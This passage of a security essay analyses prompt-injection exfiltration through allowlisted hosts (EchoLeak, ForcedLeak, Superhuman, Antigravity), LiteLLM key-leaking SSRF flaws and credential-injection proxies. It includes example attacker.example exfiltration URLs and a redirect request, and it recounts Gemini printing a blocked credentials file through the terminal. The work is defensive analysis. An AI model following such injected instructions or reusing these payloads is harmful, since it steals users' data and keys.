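Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* explains that Cowork could not function without `api.anthropic.com`, so the proxy had to allow requests to it. As intended, the proxy checked that the host was on the allowlist, but it did not check whose account would receive the data. Anthropic had thought of the list as a filter on destinations and now considers it a "capability grant", because approving a host makes every function on that host available to an attacker.

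Anthropic fixed Cowork by adding another proxy inside the VM. This "man in the middle" proxy terminates the encrypted connection, reads the request and then opens its own connection to the API. Each VM gets a session token when it starts, and the proxy forwards only requests that carry that token, so an upload with the attacker's key is blocked before it leaves the VM.

The check had to be on the user's side. Anthropic's servers could not distinguish the malicious upload from any other valid request from a paying customer. Only the VM could detect that the request came from someone else's Cowork session.

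The new proxy also blocks headers that would make Anthropic's servers fetch a URL. Without that rule, injected code might have used the VM's own valid token to make the servers fetch a URL containing the user's data. The proxy probably still has a weakness because it runs inside the VM. Code that gained full control of the VM might bypass the proxy, and the outer allowlist would still approve the host.

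Companies can get a similar check for all their Claude traffic. Anthropic's *Enforce network-level access control with Tenant Restrictions* describes a header that the company's network proxy adds to requests, listing the organisations whose accounts staff may use. Anthropic refuses requests from any other account, including requests made with an API key. The proxy has to decrypt the traffic to add the header. Anthropic tells administrators to overwrite the header on every request instead of adding it only when it is missing. Otherwise, injected code could send its own header listing the attacker's organisation. Microsoft's documentation, as recorded in Entra Diff's *Configure Custom Headers* (2026), lists an equivalent header for ChatGPT.

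This would probably have stopped the Cowork upload on an office network, because the VM ran on the user's computer. It could not have stopped Rehberger's original attack, in which the file went from one Anthropic server to another without passing through the office network.

Both checks also apply only to Anthropic's hosts. Rehberger suspected that other domains on the default list would allow similar attacks. GitHub and npm, for example, accept uploads from anyone with an account, so an attacker might supply a GitHub token in place of the Anthropic key.

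### Hosts that store what strangers send

Some hosts can pass data to an attacker without requiring a key. PromptArmor's *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails* describes an attack on the email app Superhuman, whose Content-Security-Policy blocked images from unknown sites but allowed `docs.google.com`, which Google Forms also uses. A form's owner can make a link that fills in and submits an answer through a GET request.

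The attacker created a Google form and sent the victim an email with hidden instructions. The victim didn't have to open the email. When the victim asked for a summary of recent mail, Superhuman's AI read it, put the contents of other messages into a link that would submit the form, and displayed the link as an image. The victim's browser requested the link to load the image, which submitted the messages to the attacker's form. A single response leaked parts of more than 40 emails.

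Superhuman received the report on a Friday night, disabled the vulnerable features on Monday and released a first patch on Tuesday. Four months later, PromptArmor's *Codex Exfiltrates Connector Data* reported the same attack, using a Google form, against OpenAI's Codex. OpenAI has since fixed the vulnerability.

The browser in Google's coding tool Antigravity could open only approved sites, but PromptArmor's *Google Antigravity Exfiltrates Data* reports that the default list included `webhook.site`. Developers use that site to test software that sends web requests. Anyone can create an address there and read every request sent to it, so an attacker could use one to collect stolen data.

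PromptArmor instructed Gemini, the Google model in Antigravity, to collect code and cloud credentials and open a `webhook.site` URL containing them. It put the instructions in 1-point text on a web page presented as a guide to connecting to an Oracle product. A setting should have kept Gemini from reading the credentials file, but when its file-reading tool was blocked, Gemini printed the file with a terminal command. Google warned users about data theft when they first opened Antigravity, and PromptArmor published without a private report because Google already knew of the risk. Willison noted in November 2025 that Google's page for bug hunters listed such attacks as "known issues" that Google was working to fix.

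An attacker can receive data even through a host that only counts requests. The coding agent Claude Code let its fetch tool open any page on `huggingface.co`, a site where anyone can publish AI models, without asking the user. According to GitLab's *CVE-2026-54316* (2026), Hugging Face counts requests for certain files as downloads of the model they belong to. An attacker could publish a set of models, give each one a meaning, as ZombieAgent did with its URLs, and read the message from which download counts rose. Anthropic fixed this in Claude Code 2.1.163.

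Google had faced an early version of the problem in 2023. Its chatbot Bard loaded images only from `*.google.com`, where the asterisk stands for any subdomain. Willison explains in *Hacking Google Bard* that one of those subdomains was `script.google.com`, where customers can run their own programs. A researcher used a program there to collect the data.

### Hosts that request a second address

Many services fetch URLs for their users, for instance to show a preview of a link. If such a service is on an allowlist, an attacker can put another address inside the approved one:

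`https://preview.allowed.example/fetch?url=https://attacker.example/secret`

The browser permits the request because `preview.allowed.example` is on its policy's list. The preview service then requests the second address from its own servers, where the browser's policy has no effect. The attacker uses the service because it is on the list. This is a form of SSRF, except that the attacker wants the service to contact a public server.

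*Breaking down 'EchoLeak', the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration* (Ravia, 2025) describes how the security company Aim used this against Microsoft 365 Copilot, an assistant that can search an employee's mail and files. The attack started with an email that got past Microsoft's prompt injection filter because its instructions seemed to be for the human recipient. The researchers repeated the instructions under many headings, such as "HR FAQs" and "leave of absence management", so that Copilot would retrieve the email for a wide range of questions.

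The instructions made Copilot put the most sensitive information it had found into an image URL. Copilot normally removed images from outside sites, but it missed those written in a variant of Markdown that puts the URL on a separate line. The last obstacle was the image policy, which allowed images only from a list of hosts, most of them Microsoft's.

The researchers first found a SharePoint page that fetched a URL from its query string, but it worked only if the victim had accepted an invitation to the attacker's site. They then found a Teams address that needed no invitation. A Microsoft employee quoted by SC Media describes it as a proxy that retrieves and stores external images for link previews. Microsoft fixed the flaw and told Aim that it had not affected any customers.

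Ravia printed the whole image policy, which included `*.bing.com`. A year later, Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026) showed that Bing could pass on data in the same way. Bing lets people search by image URL, and its servers fetch the image from wherever the URL points.

SearchLeak started with a link to Copilot's search page that had instructions in the query. When the victim clicked it, Copilot treated the query as a prompt, searched the mailbox and wrote an HTML image tag. The tag's URL pointed to Bing and contained the attacker's address with an email's title in it. Microsoft's software was supposed to turn such tags into harmless text, but did so only after Copilot had finished writing. The browser displayed the answer as it arrived, so it had already requested the image from Bing. Bing then requested the attacker's address, and in Varonis' example the attacker's log received an email title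 with a security code in it. Microsoft rated the flaw critical, according to The Next Web, and has fixed it.

Microsoft could have prevented the last step of SearchLeak by checking every host on the list for this behaviour after EchoLeak. Aim had already shown that two of those hosts behaved this way.

### A listed domain that anyone could buy

A domain can change owners while it remains on an allowlist. Salesforce's Agentforce, a set of AI agents for sales and customer service, allowed images from `my-salesforce-cms.com`, but Salesforce had let the domain's registration lapse. Researchers at Noma Security bought it while it was still on the allowlist. BeyondMachines' *Critical flaw in Salesforce Agentforce enables data exfiltration through AI agent exploitation* reports that they paid $5.

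They called their attack ForcedLeak. The researchers entered instructions in Web-to-Lead, a form that lets strangers send their contact details to a company's sales team. The instructions, which Willison reproduces, first ask about the number of leads and about mixing red and yellow. They then request the leads' email addresses and an image with those addresses in its URL. When an employee asked Agentforce about the new lead, it also carried out the instructions. In a passage quoted by Salesforce Ben, Noma considers the expired domain essential because the image policy would have blocked any other server the researchers controlled.

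The Hacker News (2025) reports that Salesforce took back the domain and stopped its agents from sending output to untrusted URLs. The new rule took effect on 8 September 2025. TechNadu's *Salesforce to Enforce Trusted URLs for Agentforce and Einstein AI* adds that each customer's administrators must list the external domains their agents need.

This makes thousands of administrators responsible for choosing safe hosts, and they may not know what to look for. Salesforce's *Add Trusted URLs for Agentforce Coworker (Beta)* gives `https://docs.google.com` as an example of a URL to trust, the same host through which Superhuman's emails leaked. Nobody has reported the Google Forms attack against that product, but an administrator who copied the example would have approved the host the attack needs.

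An attacker can also succeed without an expired domain if the software compares host names incorrectly. Corgea's *Claude Code has a Domain Validation Bypass* describes a version of Claude Code that checked only whether a host started with a trusted name. The host `modelcontextprotocol.io.example.com` starts with the name of a trusted site but belongs to whoever owns `example.com`, so software has to compare the whole host name.

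### What each repair would have stopped

The table compares four repairs. "Partly" means that the repair would have blocked the attack as published but left a similar one open.

| Attack | Allow only certain paths and methods | Refuse credentials the owner did not issue | Check nested addresses | Audit who controls each host |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Uploads to Anthropic's API | Partly | Yes | No | No |
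| Google Forms (Superhuman) | Yes | No | No | No |
| `webhook.site` (Antigravity) | Yes, if the path is the user's own | No | No | Probably |
| Hugging Face download counts | Yes, if the paths exclude strangers' models | No | No | No |
| Teams and Bing (EchoLeak, SearchLeak) | Yes | No | Yes | No |
| Expired domain (ForcedLeak) | No | No | No | Yes |

Path rules would have helped most often. Superhuman could have allowed the part of `docs.google.com` it needed without allowing forms. Method rules are weaker, because nearly all of these attacks used GET. A method rule would have blocked the upload to Anthropic, but an agent that can send prompts to an API can still put private data in a prompt. Rehberger's first idea was to do that with the attacker's API key. On GitHub, blocking POST would stop repository downloads as well as uploads, because Git uses POST for both over `https`. The operator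 would have to distinguish them by path.

Path rules are also harder to enforce than a list of hosts. A forward proxy has to decrypt `https` traffic to apply them. A browser can already read the path, but trackr.live's *The Model Writes the URL That Leaks Your Data* notes that browsers deliberately ignore the path in an image policy after a redirect. A browser would therefore load an image from a forbidden path on an approved host if an approved URL redirected there. The article recommends identifying a destination by host, path and resource owner, such as the company's own storage folder on a shared cloud service.

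Refusing foreign credentials is the most precise fix for the Anthropic case, and it doesn't require the proxy to judge the content. A proxy could instead replace the key with the user's own, as some later proxies do, so that the file would go to the user's account. Either way, the proxy has to check every place where a credential can appear. Cloud storage services accept uploads through signed URLs, which carry the permission in the query string, so a proxy that checked only the usual headers would miss an attacker's signed URL. Checking credentials also doesn't help with hosts that accept data from anyone.

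To check nested addresses, the software has to find and decode every URL inside the requested one, which may be encoded in several layers, and check each host against the allowlist. That would have caught the Teams and Bing requests, which contained the attacker's address in readable form. It could miss an address in an encoding the software can't decode, or a URL on an approved host that redirects elsewhere. If the application doesn't need the service that fetches URLs, blocking that service is simpler and safer.

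The application must inspect the model's output before displaying any of it, because a browser's image policy does not examine the query string. In SearchLeak, Microsoft's clean-up ran a moment too late. According to trackr.live, a company that inspects URLs in its own proxy must also protect the logs, which will contain the stolen codes and messages.

Of the repairs in the table, only an ownership audit works against ForcedLeak, because whoever owns a host can accept data at any path. The audit has to be repeated, since a registration can lapse a week later. Auditors should also check what a stranger can do on each host. Anyone can create an address on `webhook.site` and see the requests sent to it, even if the site's owner is honest. Anthropic's *Network requirements* describes another safeguard in its newer product Claude Science, which always blocks a built-in list of domains and also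 has a list of permitted domains that users can adjust.

OpenAI's check of whole URLs would have stopped the Google Forms, Teams and Bing requests, because the private data made each URL new. It would probably not have stopped the Hugging Face attack, which could use ordinary public URLs.

### What an allowlist still achieves

Host allowlists are still useful despite these bypasses. The best evidence comes from a test that Anthropic ran on its own staff in February 2026. A researcher sent an employee a friendly email with a prompt to paste into Claude Code. The prompt included, among routine steps, an instruction to read the employee's Amazon credentials, encode them and send them to an outside server. Anthropic repeated the prompt 25 times, and Claude sent the credentials 24 times.

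Anthropic concludes that only limits on network traffic and file access work when the instruction comes from the user, as it did here. An allowlist that omitted the attacker's server would have blocked all 24 requests.

Superhuman's email app loaded images only from approved hosts, so PromptArmor had to discover that one of them, Google Forms, accepts answers by GET. The company's newer assistant, Superhuman Go, had no such restriction, and PromptArmor loaded an image from its own server. The email app's list didn't stop the attack, but it made the attack harder to find and gave Superhuman a specific entry to fix.

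A list is also short enough for people to review. The Copilot policy that Ravia printed has 29 different entries. Eleven, including those for SharePoint, Teams and Bing, use an asterisk to cover any number of subdomains, so they would have been a good place to start an audit. Fourteen entries appear twice, which suggests that nobody had checked the list carefully for some time. Willison calls it "a tricky proposition" to find domains that cannot leak data, and these cases support that, but people can review 29 entries far more easily than the whole web.

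The allowlist has to cover every way the AI can send a request, though. Superhuman's email app restricted images, but its AI could open any URL through a web search feature, which PromptArmor also used to leak data. Cowork has a similar gap by design. Cloud Security Alliance's *Top 6 Claude Cowork Security Risks to Watch* warns that Cowork's web search and web fetch tools bypass the network allowlist, and advises companies to turn off web search unless they need it.

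## LiteLLM: a gateway that sent its owner's keys where callers asked

LiteLLM, a widely used gateway to AI models, sent its owner's keys to hosts that callers chose. This was the reverse of the attack on Claude Cowork, in which an attacker's key went to a host that Anthropic had approved. LiteLLM's developers fixed the flaw in 2024, but two years later researchers were still finding other ways to make the gateway send its owner's keys to such hosts.

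### How LiteLLM picks a server and a key

LiteLLM is an open-source gateway that gives a company one address for models from OpenAI, Anthropic, Amazon and many other providers. The company stores its provider keys in the gateway and gives staff and applications separate keys that work only there. It can then set budgets and cancel one person's access without replacing its OpenAI key. Administrators control the gateway with a master key.

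For each model the operator writes a record, roughly like this:

```
name:      support-chat
model:     openai/gpt-6-luna
api_base:  https://api.openai.com/v1
api_key:   (the company's OpenAI key)
```

An application sends a prompt and the name `support-chat`. LiteLLM finds the record with that name, attaches the key and forwards the prompt to the address in `api_base`. If the address and the key both come from the record, the application cannot change where the key goes.

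GitLab's *CVE-2024-6587* (2024) describes how callers got that influence. LiteLLM also accepted `api_base` in the request itself, and the caller's address replaced the operator's. The key stayed the same. In outline:

```
Caller to gateway
    POST /chat/completions
    key:       the caller's gateway key
    model:     support-chat
    api_base:  https://attacker.example

Gateway to attacker.example
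    POST /chat/completions
    key:       the company's OpenAI key
```

The attacker reads the OpenAI key in their own server log. Neither encryption nor a filter for internal addresses would stop this, because `attacker.example` is a public host with a valid certificate.

This is the same flaw as in Hardy's compiler, except that the caller supplies an address instead of a file name. Hardy's user could make the compiler overwrite a file but never obtained the compiler's permission to write there. The consequences are worse with LiteLLM because the caller obtained the key itself and could use it directly with OpenAI, outside the gateway's budgets and logs, until somebody cancelled it.

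### The first repair

The developers responded by adding a check that ran before the gateway handled a request. In LiteLLM's code from September 2024, the check rejected any request whose body contained a field called `api_base` or `base_url`, unless the operator had allowed such fields for the whole gateway or for that model.

The check also exempted callers who sent their own `api_key`, since they wouldn't need the operator's. But the code tested only whether the field was there, and some providers use more than one credential. The developers knew this and withheld the exemption from models on Amazon's Bedrock and SageMaker and Google's Vertex AI, which the code recognised by looking for words such as `vertex_ai` in the model name. But callers use whatever name the operator picked. In one example in LiteLLM's documentation, a Vertex model is called `gemini-2.5-flash`, which this test would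 have missed.

A bigger gap was that the check read only the top level of the request. Several of LiteLLM's endpoints expect the same settings one level down, inside an object called `litellm_params`:

```
api_base: https://attacker.example          refused

litellm_params:
    api_base: https://attacker.example      missed
```

The security company Escape tested this in April 2026 and calls it "a flat check in a nested world". Two endpoints for testing a connection accepted the nested address. Both required an administrator's key, but one returned the other server's response inside its error message, so a caller could use it to read pages on the internal network. The comments in the code show that the developers wrote the check for `/chat/completions`, where it did block the published attack, so Escape isn't quite right to describe it as broken on the endpoint it was written for.

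Any logged-in user, not just an administrator, could exploit the most accessible flaw Escape found. An endpoint that adds documents to a searchable collection accepted a `file_url` and fetched it without checking where it led. The check missed this because the name `file_url` was not on the list.

Escape counted a flaw as real only if a request arrived at a server it controlled. This rule kept the team from mistaking a validation failure for an attempted connection. When the team first pointed the ingestion endpoint at the cloud metadata address, the gateway hung for five seconds, but the request had failed validation before reaching the code that fetches files. Padilla's timing result for another server, described earlier, could have a similar explanation.

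The ingestion endpoint made an ordinary GET request without a provider key, so an attacker could send requests from the gateway's position on the network but did not get its credentials. Escape's evidence does not fully support its claim that the attacker could then steal cloud credentials on any large cloud. The test machine was not on Amazon's cloud, Escape classes the flaw as "blind" (the caller doesn't see the response), and Amazon's newer metadata service would reject a plain GET. LiteLLM's maintainers told Escape they already knew about the problem. Escape gives no CVE number or fixed version.

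### Attempts against live gateways

Attackers were trying to exploit CVE-2024-6587 well before then. On 9 March 2025, GreyNoise (2025), a company that monitors internet scanning, recorded attempts from about 400 IP addresses to exploit ten SSRF flaws, including this one and others in products such as GitLab and VMware. Many of the addresses were used to try several exploits, so some of the attackers were probably trying every exploit they had on every server they found. GreyNoise doesn't give a separate number for LiteLLM.

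Zenity Labs' *Threat Actors Are Trying to Turn LiteLLM's Connection-Test Into a Key-Exfiltration Channel* reports attacks aimed at LiteLLM. Zenity ran honeypots, decoy servers that record what attackers send. Between 7 April and 1 June 2026, the honeypots received 2,721 requests from 21 IP addresses. Of these requests, 2,704 went to `/health/test_connection`, one of the two endpoints where Escape had found the nested address. All 2,704 carried the same false browser identification, and each IP address was active on only one day, so Zenity attributes the requests to a single automated tool.

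These requests set `api_base` to the attacker's address. In place of a key, they gave a reference to the environment variable (a named value that a program reads from its surroundings) that holds the gateway's master key. LiteLLM lets operators use such references in their settings file to keep secrets out of the file, but the gateway also replaced references in callers' requests with the real secrets. As a result, a request that seemed to bring its own key made the gateway send the owner's master key to the attacker.

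Zenity reproduced this on versions 1.74.0, 1.81.0 and 1.82.0. OSV's *CVE-2026-59819* (2026) covers the same resolving of references and a way to read local files, and lists version 1.83.10 as the fix. The vulnerability scores only 2.1 out of 10, largely because the caller needs administrator rights. Zenity's tests show that this requirement doesn't protect a gateway with no master key, which accepts anyone. Some operators may also have made the requirement ineffective by keeping `sk-1234`, the example key in LiteLLM's documentation, which the attackers sent.

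If the master key is `sk-1234`, the attacker receives a key they already had, and if there is no master key, there is presumably nothing to send. Zenity doesn't discuss this oddity, but the requests make more sense as a search for gateways that leak secrets. A second request to such a gateway could name the variable that holds the OpenAI key. The targets were decoys, so the figures are for attempts, and nobody has reported how many real gateways leaked keys this way.

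### CVE-2026-84377

The developers then adopted a better defence. According to the *v1.84.0* release notes, LiteLLM now drops the operator's credentials whenever a request changes `api_base` or `base_url`. An attacker who redirects a request should then receive their own prompt and no key.

The same release added nine names to the list of forbidden fields, including fields for the addresses of logging services and a Slack notification hook. It also removed the exception for callers who sent an `api_key`. Between the release candidate and the final version, the developers had to extend the check to an object called `extra_body`. They also fixed how LiteLLM guessed a provider from a URL. It had looked for the provider's address anywhere in the URL, much as Claude Code once accepted any host that began with a trusted name.

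Dropping the credentials works only if the gateway notices that the address has changed. OSV's *CVE-2026-84377* (2026), published on 2 September, explains that any logged-in user could still redirect a call and receive the operator's credentials, because the checks missed the change when callers wrote it in other ways:

- Callers could put the address in a nested field that the check did not inspect.
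- They could supply values in the URL's path, while the check read only the body. A note in the 2024 code had already reminded the developers that the check ignored model names in the URL.
- They could send a web form with brackets in a field's name. A form is a flat list of names and values, and `settings[address]` is a conventional way to write a field called `address` inside `settings`.
- They could use fields such as `model_list` and `fallbacks`, which can hold whole model records with addresses of their own.
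- They could use `litellm_credential_name` to select one of the operator's stored credentials by name.

The last of these differs from the original attack because the caller picks the key instead of the address. According to LiteLLM's *v1.97.0rc1*, the gateway now uses each stored credential only with its own endpoint, so nobody can test a connection with a different model's key.

The newer flaw scores 6.5 and the 2024 one 7.5, only because the newer attack requires a login; the rated damage is identical. A login is a modest obstacle on a gateway meant to give keys to staff and applications. An attacker could also inject instructions into an agent that holds a gateway key and can send web requests, and have the agent carry out the attack.

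| Flaw in LiteLLM | Affected versions | Fixed in |
|---|---|---|
| CVE-2024-6587, address in the request | All before 1.44.8 | 1.44.8 |
| CVE-2026-59819, secret and file references in the connection test | All before 1.83.10 | 1.83.10 |
| CVE-2026-84377, address or credential in places the checks missed | All before 1.88.6, and 1.89.0 up to 1.96.2 | 1.88.6 and 1.96.2, with repairs to the series in between |

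The main record for CVE-2026-84377 lists only two fixed versions. HOL Guard, a security product's vulnerability list, adds seven more, one for each series from 1.89 (fixed in 1.89.7) to 1.95 (fixed in 1.95.1). A scanner that relies only on the main record may flag a patched gateway as vulnerable. Operators also can't assume every later version is safe, because LiteLLM (2026) announced that release 1.107.0 of 21 October had been compromised. OffSeq's *CVE-2026-84377* (2026) listed no known exploitation of the September flaw as of 1 December.

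### Why the list kept missing cases

The check and the rest of the gateway read each request separately. The check looked for certain names in certain places, while the code that sent the request assembled its settings from every place it was written to read. A caller could get an address past the check wherever the two readings differed. The fetch server that mishandled IPv6 brackets also read each URL in two ways that could differ.

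A complete list has to cover every name for a destination, in every position and format. Ten names, three positions and two formats make 60 combinations, and each new name adds six. Developers of a busy project often add names without thinking of them as security changes, and the release candidate for 1.97.0 alone contains 252 sets of code changes. The names that the list missed include `file_url` and `spec_path`, the latter of which specifies where LiteLLM finds a tool's description. The NixOS entry for CVE-2026-12798 reports SSRF through `spec_path` in versions up to 1.82.2.

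A list of permitted fields would be safer than a list of forbidden ones, because the gateway would refuse any field that nobody had considered. But it would also stop LiteLLM from passing unfamiliar fields on to the provider, which it does deliberately so that users can try a provider's new features on the day they appear. The forbidden list is still growing. According to LiteLLM's *Clientside LLM Credentials*, since version 1.111.0 the gateway also refuses four fields that select a Google region or project, unless the operator allows them.

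There are very many possible requests, but each ends with the gateway sending a key to an address. A check at that point only has to establish whether that key may go to that address, however the caller wrote it.

### A repository that redirected Claude Code

Claude Code had a similar flaw that didn't involve a gateway. The program normally sends its requests to Anthropic, but the environment variable `ANTHROPIC_BASE_URL` can send them to another address. Anthropic's documentation shows companies how to use this variable to route Claude Code's traffic through LiteLLM.

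Donenfeld and Vanunu of Check Point point out in *Caught in the Hook* (2026) that a software project could also set the variable. Claude Code reads a settings file in the project's folder so that everyone on a team gets the same configuration, and anyone who can change the project can change that file. The researchers pointed the variable at an interception program on their own machine and watched the traffic. Claude Code sent several requests before they had answered its question about whether they trusted the folder, and each request contained their full API key.

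An attacker therefore needed only to publish a useful-looking project with one extra line in its settings, without getting a model to follow an injected instruction. A developer who downloaded the project and started Claude Code in its folder would expose their key to the attacker before making any decision.

The key could also expose colleagues' files. Anthropic groups API keys into workspaces, and every key in a workspace has access to the files stored there. Anthropic's API doesn't return files that users uploaded, but it does return files that Claude created. Donenfeld and Vanunu asked Claude to copy an uploaded file and then downloaded the copy.

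They reported the problem on 28 October 2025, and Anthropic fixed it two months later. NVD's *CVE-2026-21852 Detail* gives 2.0.65 as the first safe version. Claude Code now sends nothing to the API until the user agrees to trust the folder.

That stops the silent theft, but as Donenfeld and Vanunu describe the fix, Claude Code still sends the user's key to the address the project chose once the user agrees. Someone may trust a project enough to work on its code without meaning to give its author an API key. Claude Code could instead ignore a project's address unless the user has approved that particular host, or refuse to send that address a key the user obtained for Anthropic.

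Anthropic's instructions for Amazon's and Google's clouds already describe a setup closer to this. When Claude Code reaches those services through a gateway, an extra setting makes it skip its own cloud login, and the gateway supplies the credentials for the server it contacts.

### One party sets the address and the key

In both programs, one party supplied the credential and another chose the destination. The fix is to require whoever supplies a credential to limit where it can be sent, and to require a caller who changes the destination to supply their own credential.

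Some of LiteLLM's code treats an address and a key as interchangeable. A file for handling "clientside credentials" lists `api_key`, `api_base` and `base_url`, and counts a request as having such a credential if it contains any one of them. An address alone therefore passes this test, although the rule requires both an address and a key.

Callers often have good reasons to name an address, so an outright ban would not last. LiteLLM added its first opt-in partly for developers who wanted to experiment with their own fine-tuned models at the provider Fireworks. The rule allows a developer to send a private model's address with the key for it, because the operator's key isn't involved. It also allows a user to send a list of models, each with its own address and key, and an administrator to test a new connection by typing in the new key.

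Sometimes the caller supplies a key and the operator sets the destination. LiteLLM's *Forward Client Headers to LLM API* describes this arrangement for companies whose customers have their own accounts with Anthropic or OpenAI. It meets the rule's purpose, which is to ensure that a key's owner approves its destination, because the customer chooses to send the key to this gateway for use with a named provider. The gateway's operator could read the key regardless of who set the destination. Read literally, the rule would still forbid the arrangement, since the customer doesn't set the destination.

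The hardest case is a caller who needs the operator's key at one of several addresses, such as a choice of regions. The operator can approve the whole set in advance. LiteLLM lets operators do this with a regular expression, a pattern that the address must match, and its documentation offers this one:

`^https://litellm.*direct\.fireworks\.ai/v1$`

The pattern's `.*` matches any characters, including slashes, so the Fireworks name can appear in the path of a URL on another party's host. Since 1.84.0 the gateway should drop the operator's credentials after such a redirect, which makes the mistake much less harmful. An operator who wants to approve four regions would still do better to list the four addresses.

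Several LiteLLM records can share a name, and the gateway picks one of them for each request. Before version 1.111.0, it applied one record's permission to the whole group, so a caller could override the address for a record whose operator had never allowed it. LiteLLM now allows the override only if it is permitted in every record in the group, including any that the request might fall back to.

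### Taking the destination from the credential's record

A gateway can follow the rule without a list of forbidden fields if it never combines a caller's address with a stored key. The logic is short:

```
if the caller names an address:
    address = the caller's address
    key     = the caller's key, or refuse
else:
    record  = the operator's record for this model
    address = record.address
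    key     = record.key
```

The function that sends requests should then accept a record, with no way to pass it an address and a stored key separately. This prevents a programmer who later adds a feature from accidentally pairing a key with the wrong address. A caller who finds a new place to hide an address also gains nothing, because no code on the second route reads an address from the request. This design resembles the capabilities that Hardy preferred to checks on file names.

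For this to work, the gateway must treat the caller's key as plain text, because resolving a reference to an environment variable would bring back the owner's secret. It must not follow a redirect to another host with the key attached. If part of the URL, such as a region, depends on the request, the gateway must choose it from fixed values, because the caller's text could contain a different host. The addresses it sends logs to need records too, since LiteLLM's forbidden list had to cover several logging services.

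Requests to addresses that callers supply can still reach the internal network, so they need the same address checks that fetch servers use. Sending them from a separate process without access to the operator's keys would be safer. An attacker who exploited a bug in that process could then at most use its network access, which the operator can restrict with a firewall.

Editing a stored model needs the most care. LiteLLM hides stored keys from people who manage models, but anyone who can change the address beside a key can have the gateway send the key to them. One request to Zenity's honeypots tried something like this by saving a new address in a stored model. The gateway should delete the key whenever somebody changes the address and require them to enter it again, which takes a minute for an administrator who has the key. This would prevent administrators who aren't supposed to have the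 key from getting it this way.

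## Fly.io's Tokenizer and later proxies that add credentials outside the sandbox

In 2023 the cloud host Fly.io published Tokenizer, a forward proxy that adds keys to requests for other companies' services. Whoever encrypts a key for Tokenizer can restrict it to a list of hosts. LiteLLM lacked this link between key and address. By 2026 several companies that run agents in sandboxes had built proxies on the same principle. The proxy adds the real credential outside the agent's reach, a technique called credential injection, so the agent can use a service without holding its key.

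### How Tokenizer handles a secret

Fly.io's main application, built with the web framework Rails, needed keys for other companies' services. *Tokenized Tokens*, the company's account of the project, explains why an ordinary secrets manager wasn't enough. Most keys work for whoever presents them, so the application would have to read a key to use it. An attacker who took over the application could read the key too.

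Tokenizer relies on public-key encryption, in which anyone can encrypt a message with a public key but only the holder of the matching private key can decrypt it. Tokenizer holds the private key, and the application holds only encrypted secrets. The project's documentation, superfly's *Tokenizer* (2023), uses the payments company Stripe as its example. Before encryption, a secret looks roughly like this:

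```
token:          (the Stripe key)
bearer_auth:    (a hash of the application's password)
allowed_hosts:  api.stripe.com
```

A hash is a fingerprint that lets a program check a password without storing it. The application calls Stripe as follows:

1. It addresses a request to `http://api.stripe.com` and sends it through Tokenizer. The encrypted secret goes in a header called `Proxy-Tokenizer`, and the application's password goes in `Proxy-Authorization`.
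2. Tokenizer decrypts the secret with its private key.
3. It hashes the password and compares the result with the stored hash. Someone who had stolen only the encrypted secret would fail this check.
4. It checks that `api.stripe.com` is on the secret's list of hosts.
5. It puts the Stripe key in an `Authorization` header and forwards the request over `https`.

The application connects to Tokenizer over plain `http` because an `https` request would go through a tunnel that Tokenizer couldn't read. The documentation therefore assumes that something else, such as a VPN, protects this connection.

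Tokenizer keeps no database of secrets. The application stores them encrypted, and Tokenizer holds the private key that decrypts them, so an attacker who copied only the application's database or only the key could not read the secrets. Tokenizer can also compute signatures for services that require a signature made with a key instead of the key itself.

Fly.io also had to keep new secrets out of the application. When a customer logs in with Google, Google gives a token to whichever program completes the login. Fly.io moved the login to a second small program, SSOkenizer, which encrypts the token for Tokenizer before the application receives it.

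### What the list of hosts prevents

Without the list, an attacker who controlled the application could get the Stripe key by sending the encrypted secret and the correct password through Tokenizer in a request addressed to their own server. Tokenizer would decrypt the key and attach it to the request, and the attacker could read it in their server's log. They could also address the request to a public echo service, which returns whatever it receives, and read the key in the response.

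The list blocks both versions. The attacker can't edit it because it is inside the encrypted secret. The public key isn't confidential, so they could encrypt a new secret with a different list, but they would need to already have the Stripe key to put in it.

The list is optional, however, and the first example in the documentation leaves it out. Tokenizer also accepts a pattern instead of a list, and the documentation suggests this one, written in the programming language Ruby:

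`".*\.stripe\.com$"`

The backslashes should make each dot match only a literal dot, but Ruby discards them in double-quoted strings. Each dot then matches any character, so `notstripe.com` passes. A list of exact names avoids this mistake.

Tokenizer also forwards requests to private addresses, so its documentation advises operators not to put it on the public internet. By default it refuses requests that carry no encrypted secret, but anyone with the public key can create an encrypted secret.

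### Placeholders in agents' sandboxes

In April 2025, Fly.io suggested using the same idea for language models. *Our Best Customers Are Now Robots* describes an agent that sorts someone's email while holding only a placeholder, useless by itself, that a separate machine replaces with the real token. In February 2026, Willison wrote about a sandbox from the software company Deno that works this way, and learned from a reader's comment that Tokenizer had done it earlier.

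Most of the later products don't use Tokenizer's encryption. Instead, the proxy stores the secret or fetches it from a secrets manager, and the sandbox gets a placeholder or nothing.

Cloudflare lets operators write a short program for each host. The program runs outside the sandbox and can change any request to that host. The example program in Cloudflare's *Dynamic, identity-aware, and secure Sandbox auth* (2026) adds a secret header, and a variant looks up a different key for each sandbox. Docker's product runs agents on a developer's computer. According to Docker's *Credentials*, the product sets the environment variables that usually hold keys to `proxy-managed`, because many client libraries won't start without something that looks like a key. A proxy outside the sandbox then overwrites the authentication header.

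The sandbox company E2B attaches headers by host, and only to `https` requests. If its proxy can't find a secret, perhaps because somebody misspelled the name, it forwards the request without the header, according to E2B's *Injecting secrets into requests*. The request will probably fail, but any data in it still reaches the host. The open-source tool fnox has the narrowest rules of the four. According to its *Credential proxy*, it replaces a placeholder only if the domain, method, path and header all match.

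| | What the sandbox holds | Where the real credential goes | Hosts without a rule |
|---|---|---|---|
| Cloudflare | Nothing | Wherever the operator's program puts it | Open, unless the operator sets an allowlist |
| Docker | A placeholder | The authentication header, or anywhere the placeholder appears for custom secrets | Subject to a separate network policy |
| E2B | Nothing | The header named in the rule | Subject to separate access settings |
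| fnox | A placeholder | The header named in the rule | Refused by default |

E2B's proxy would overwrite an attacker's own key, like the one in the Claude Cowork attack, if the key was in the configured header. A proxy that replaces placeholders would find none in such a request, so it would have nothing to replace. A longer edition of the fnox documentation explains how to recognise requests in its log that went through without a placeholder.

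### One request through an injecting proxy

Suppose the user now asks the agent to reserve *Middlemarch*. The library's reservation service requires a token, which the operator has stored in a proxy with a rule like this:

```
secret:   LIBRARY_TOKEN
domain:   api.library.example
header:   authorization
methods:  POST
paths:    /reservations
```

The agent runs a program that reads `LIBRARY_TOKEN` from its environment and gets `placeholder-51c8`. The program prepares this request:

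```
POST /reservations HTTP/1.1
Host: api.library.example
Authorization: Bearer placeholder-51c8
```

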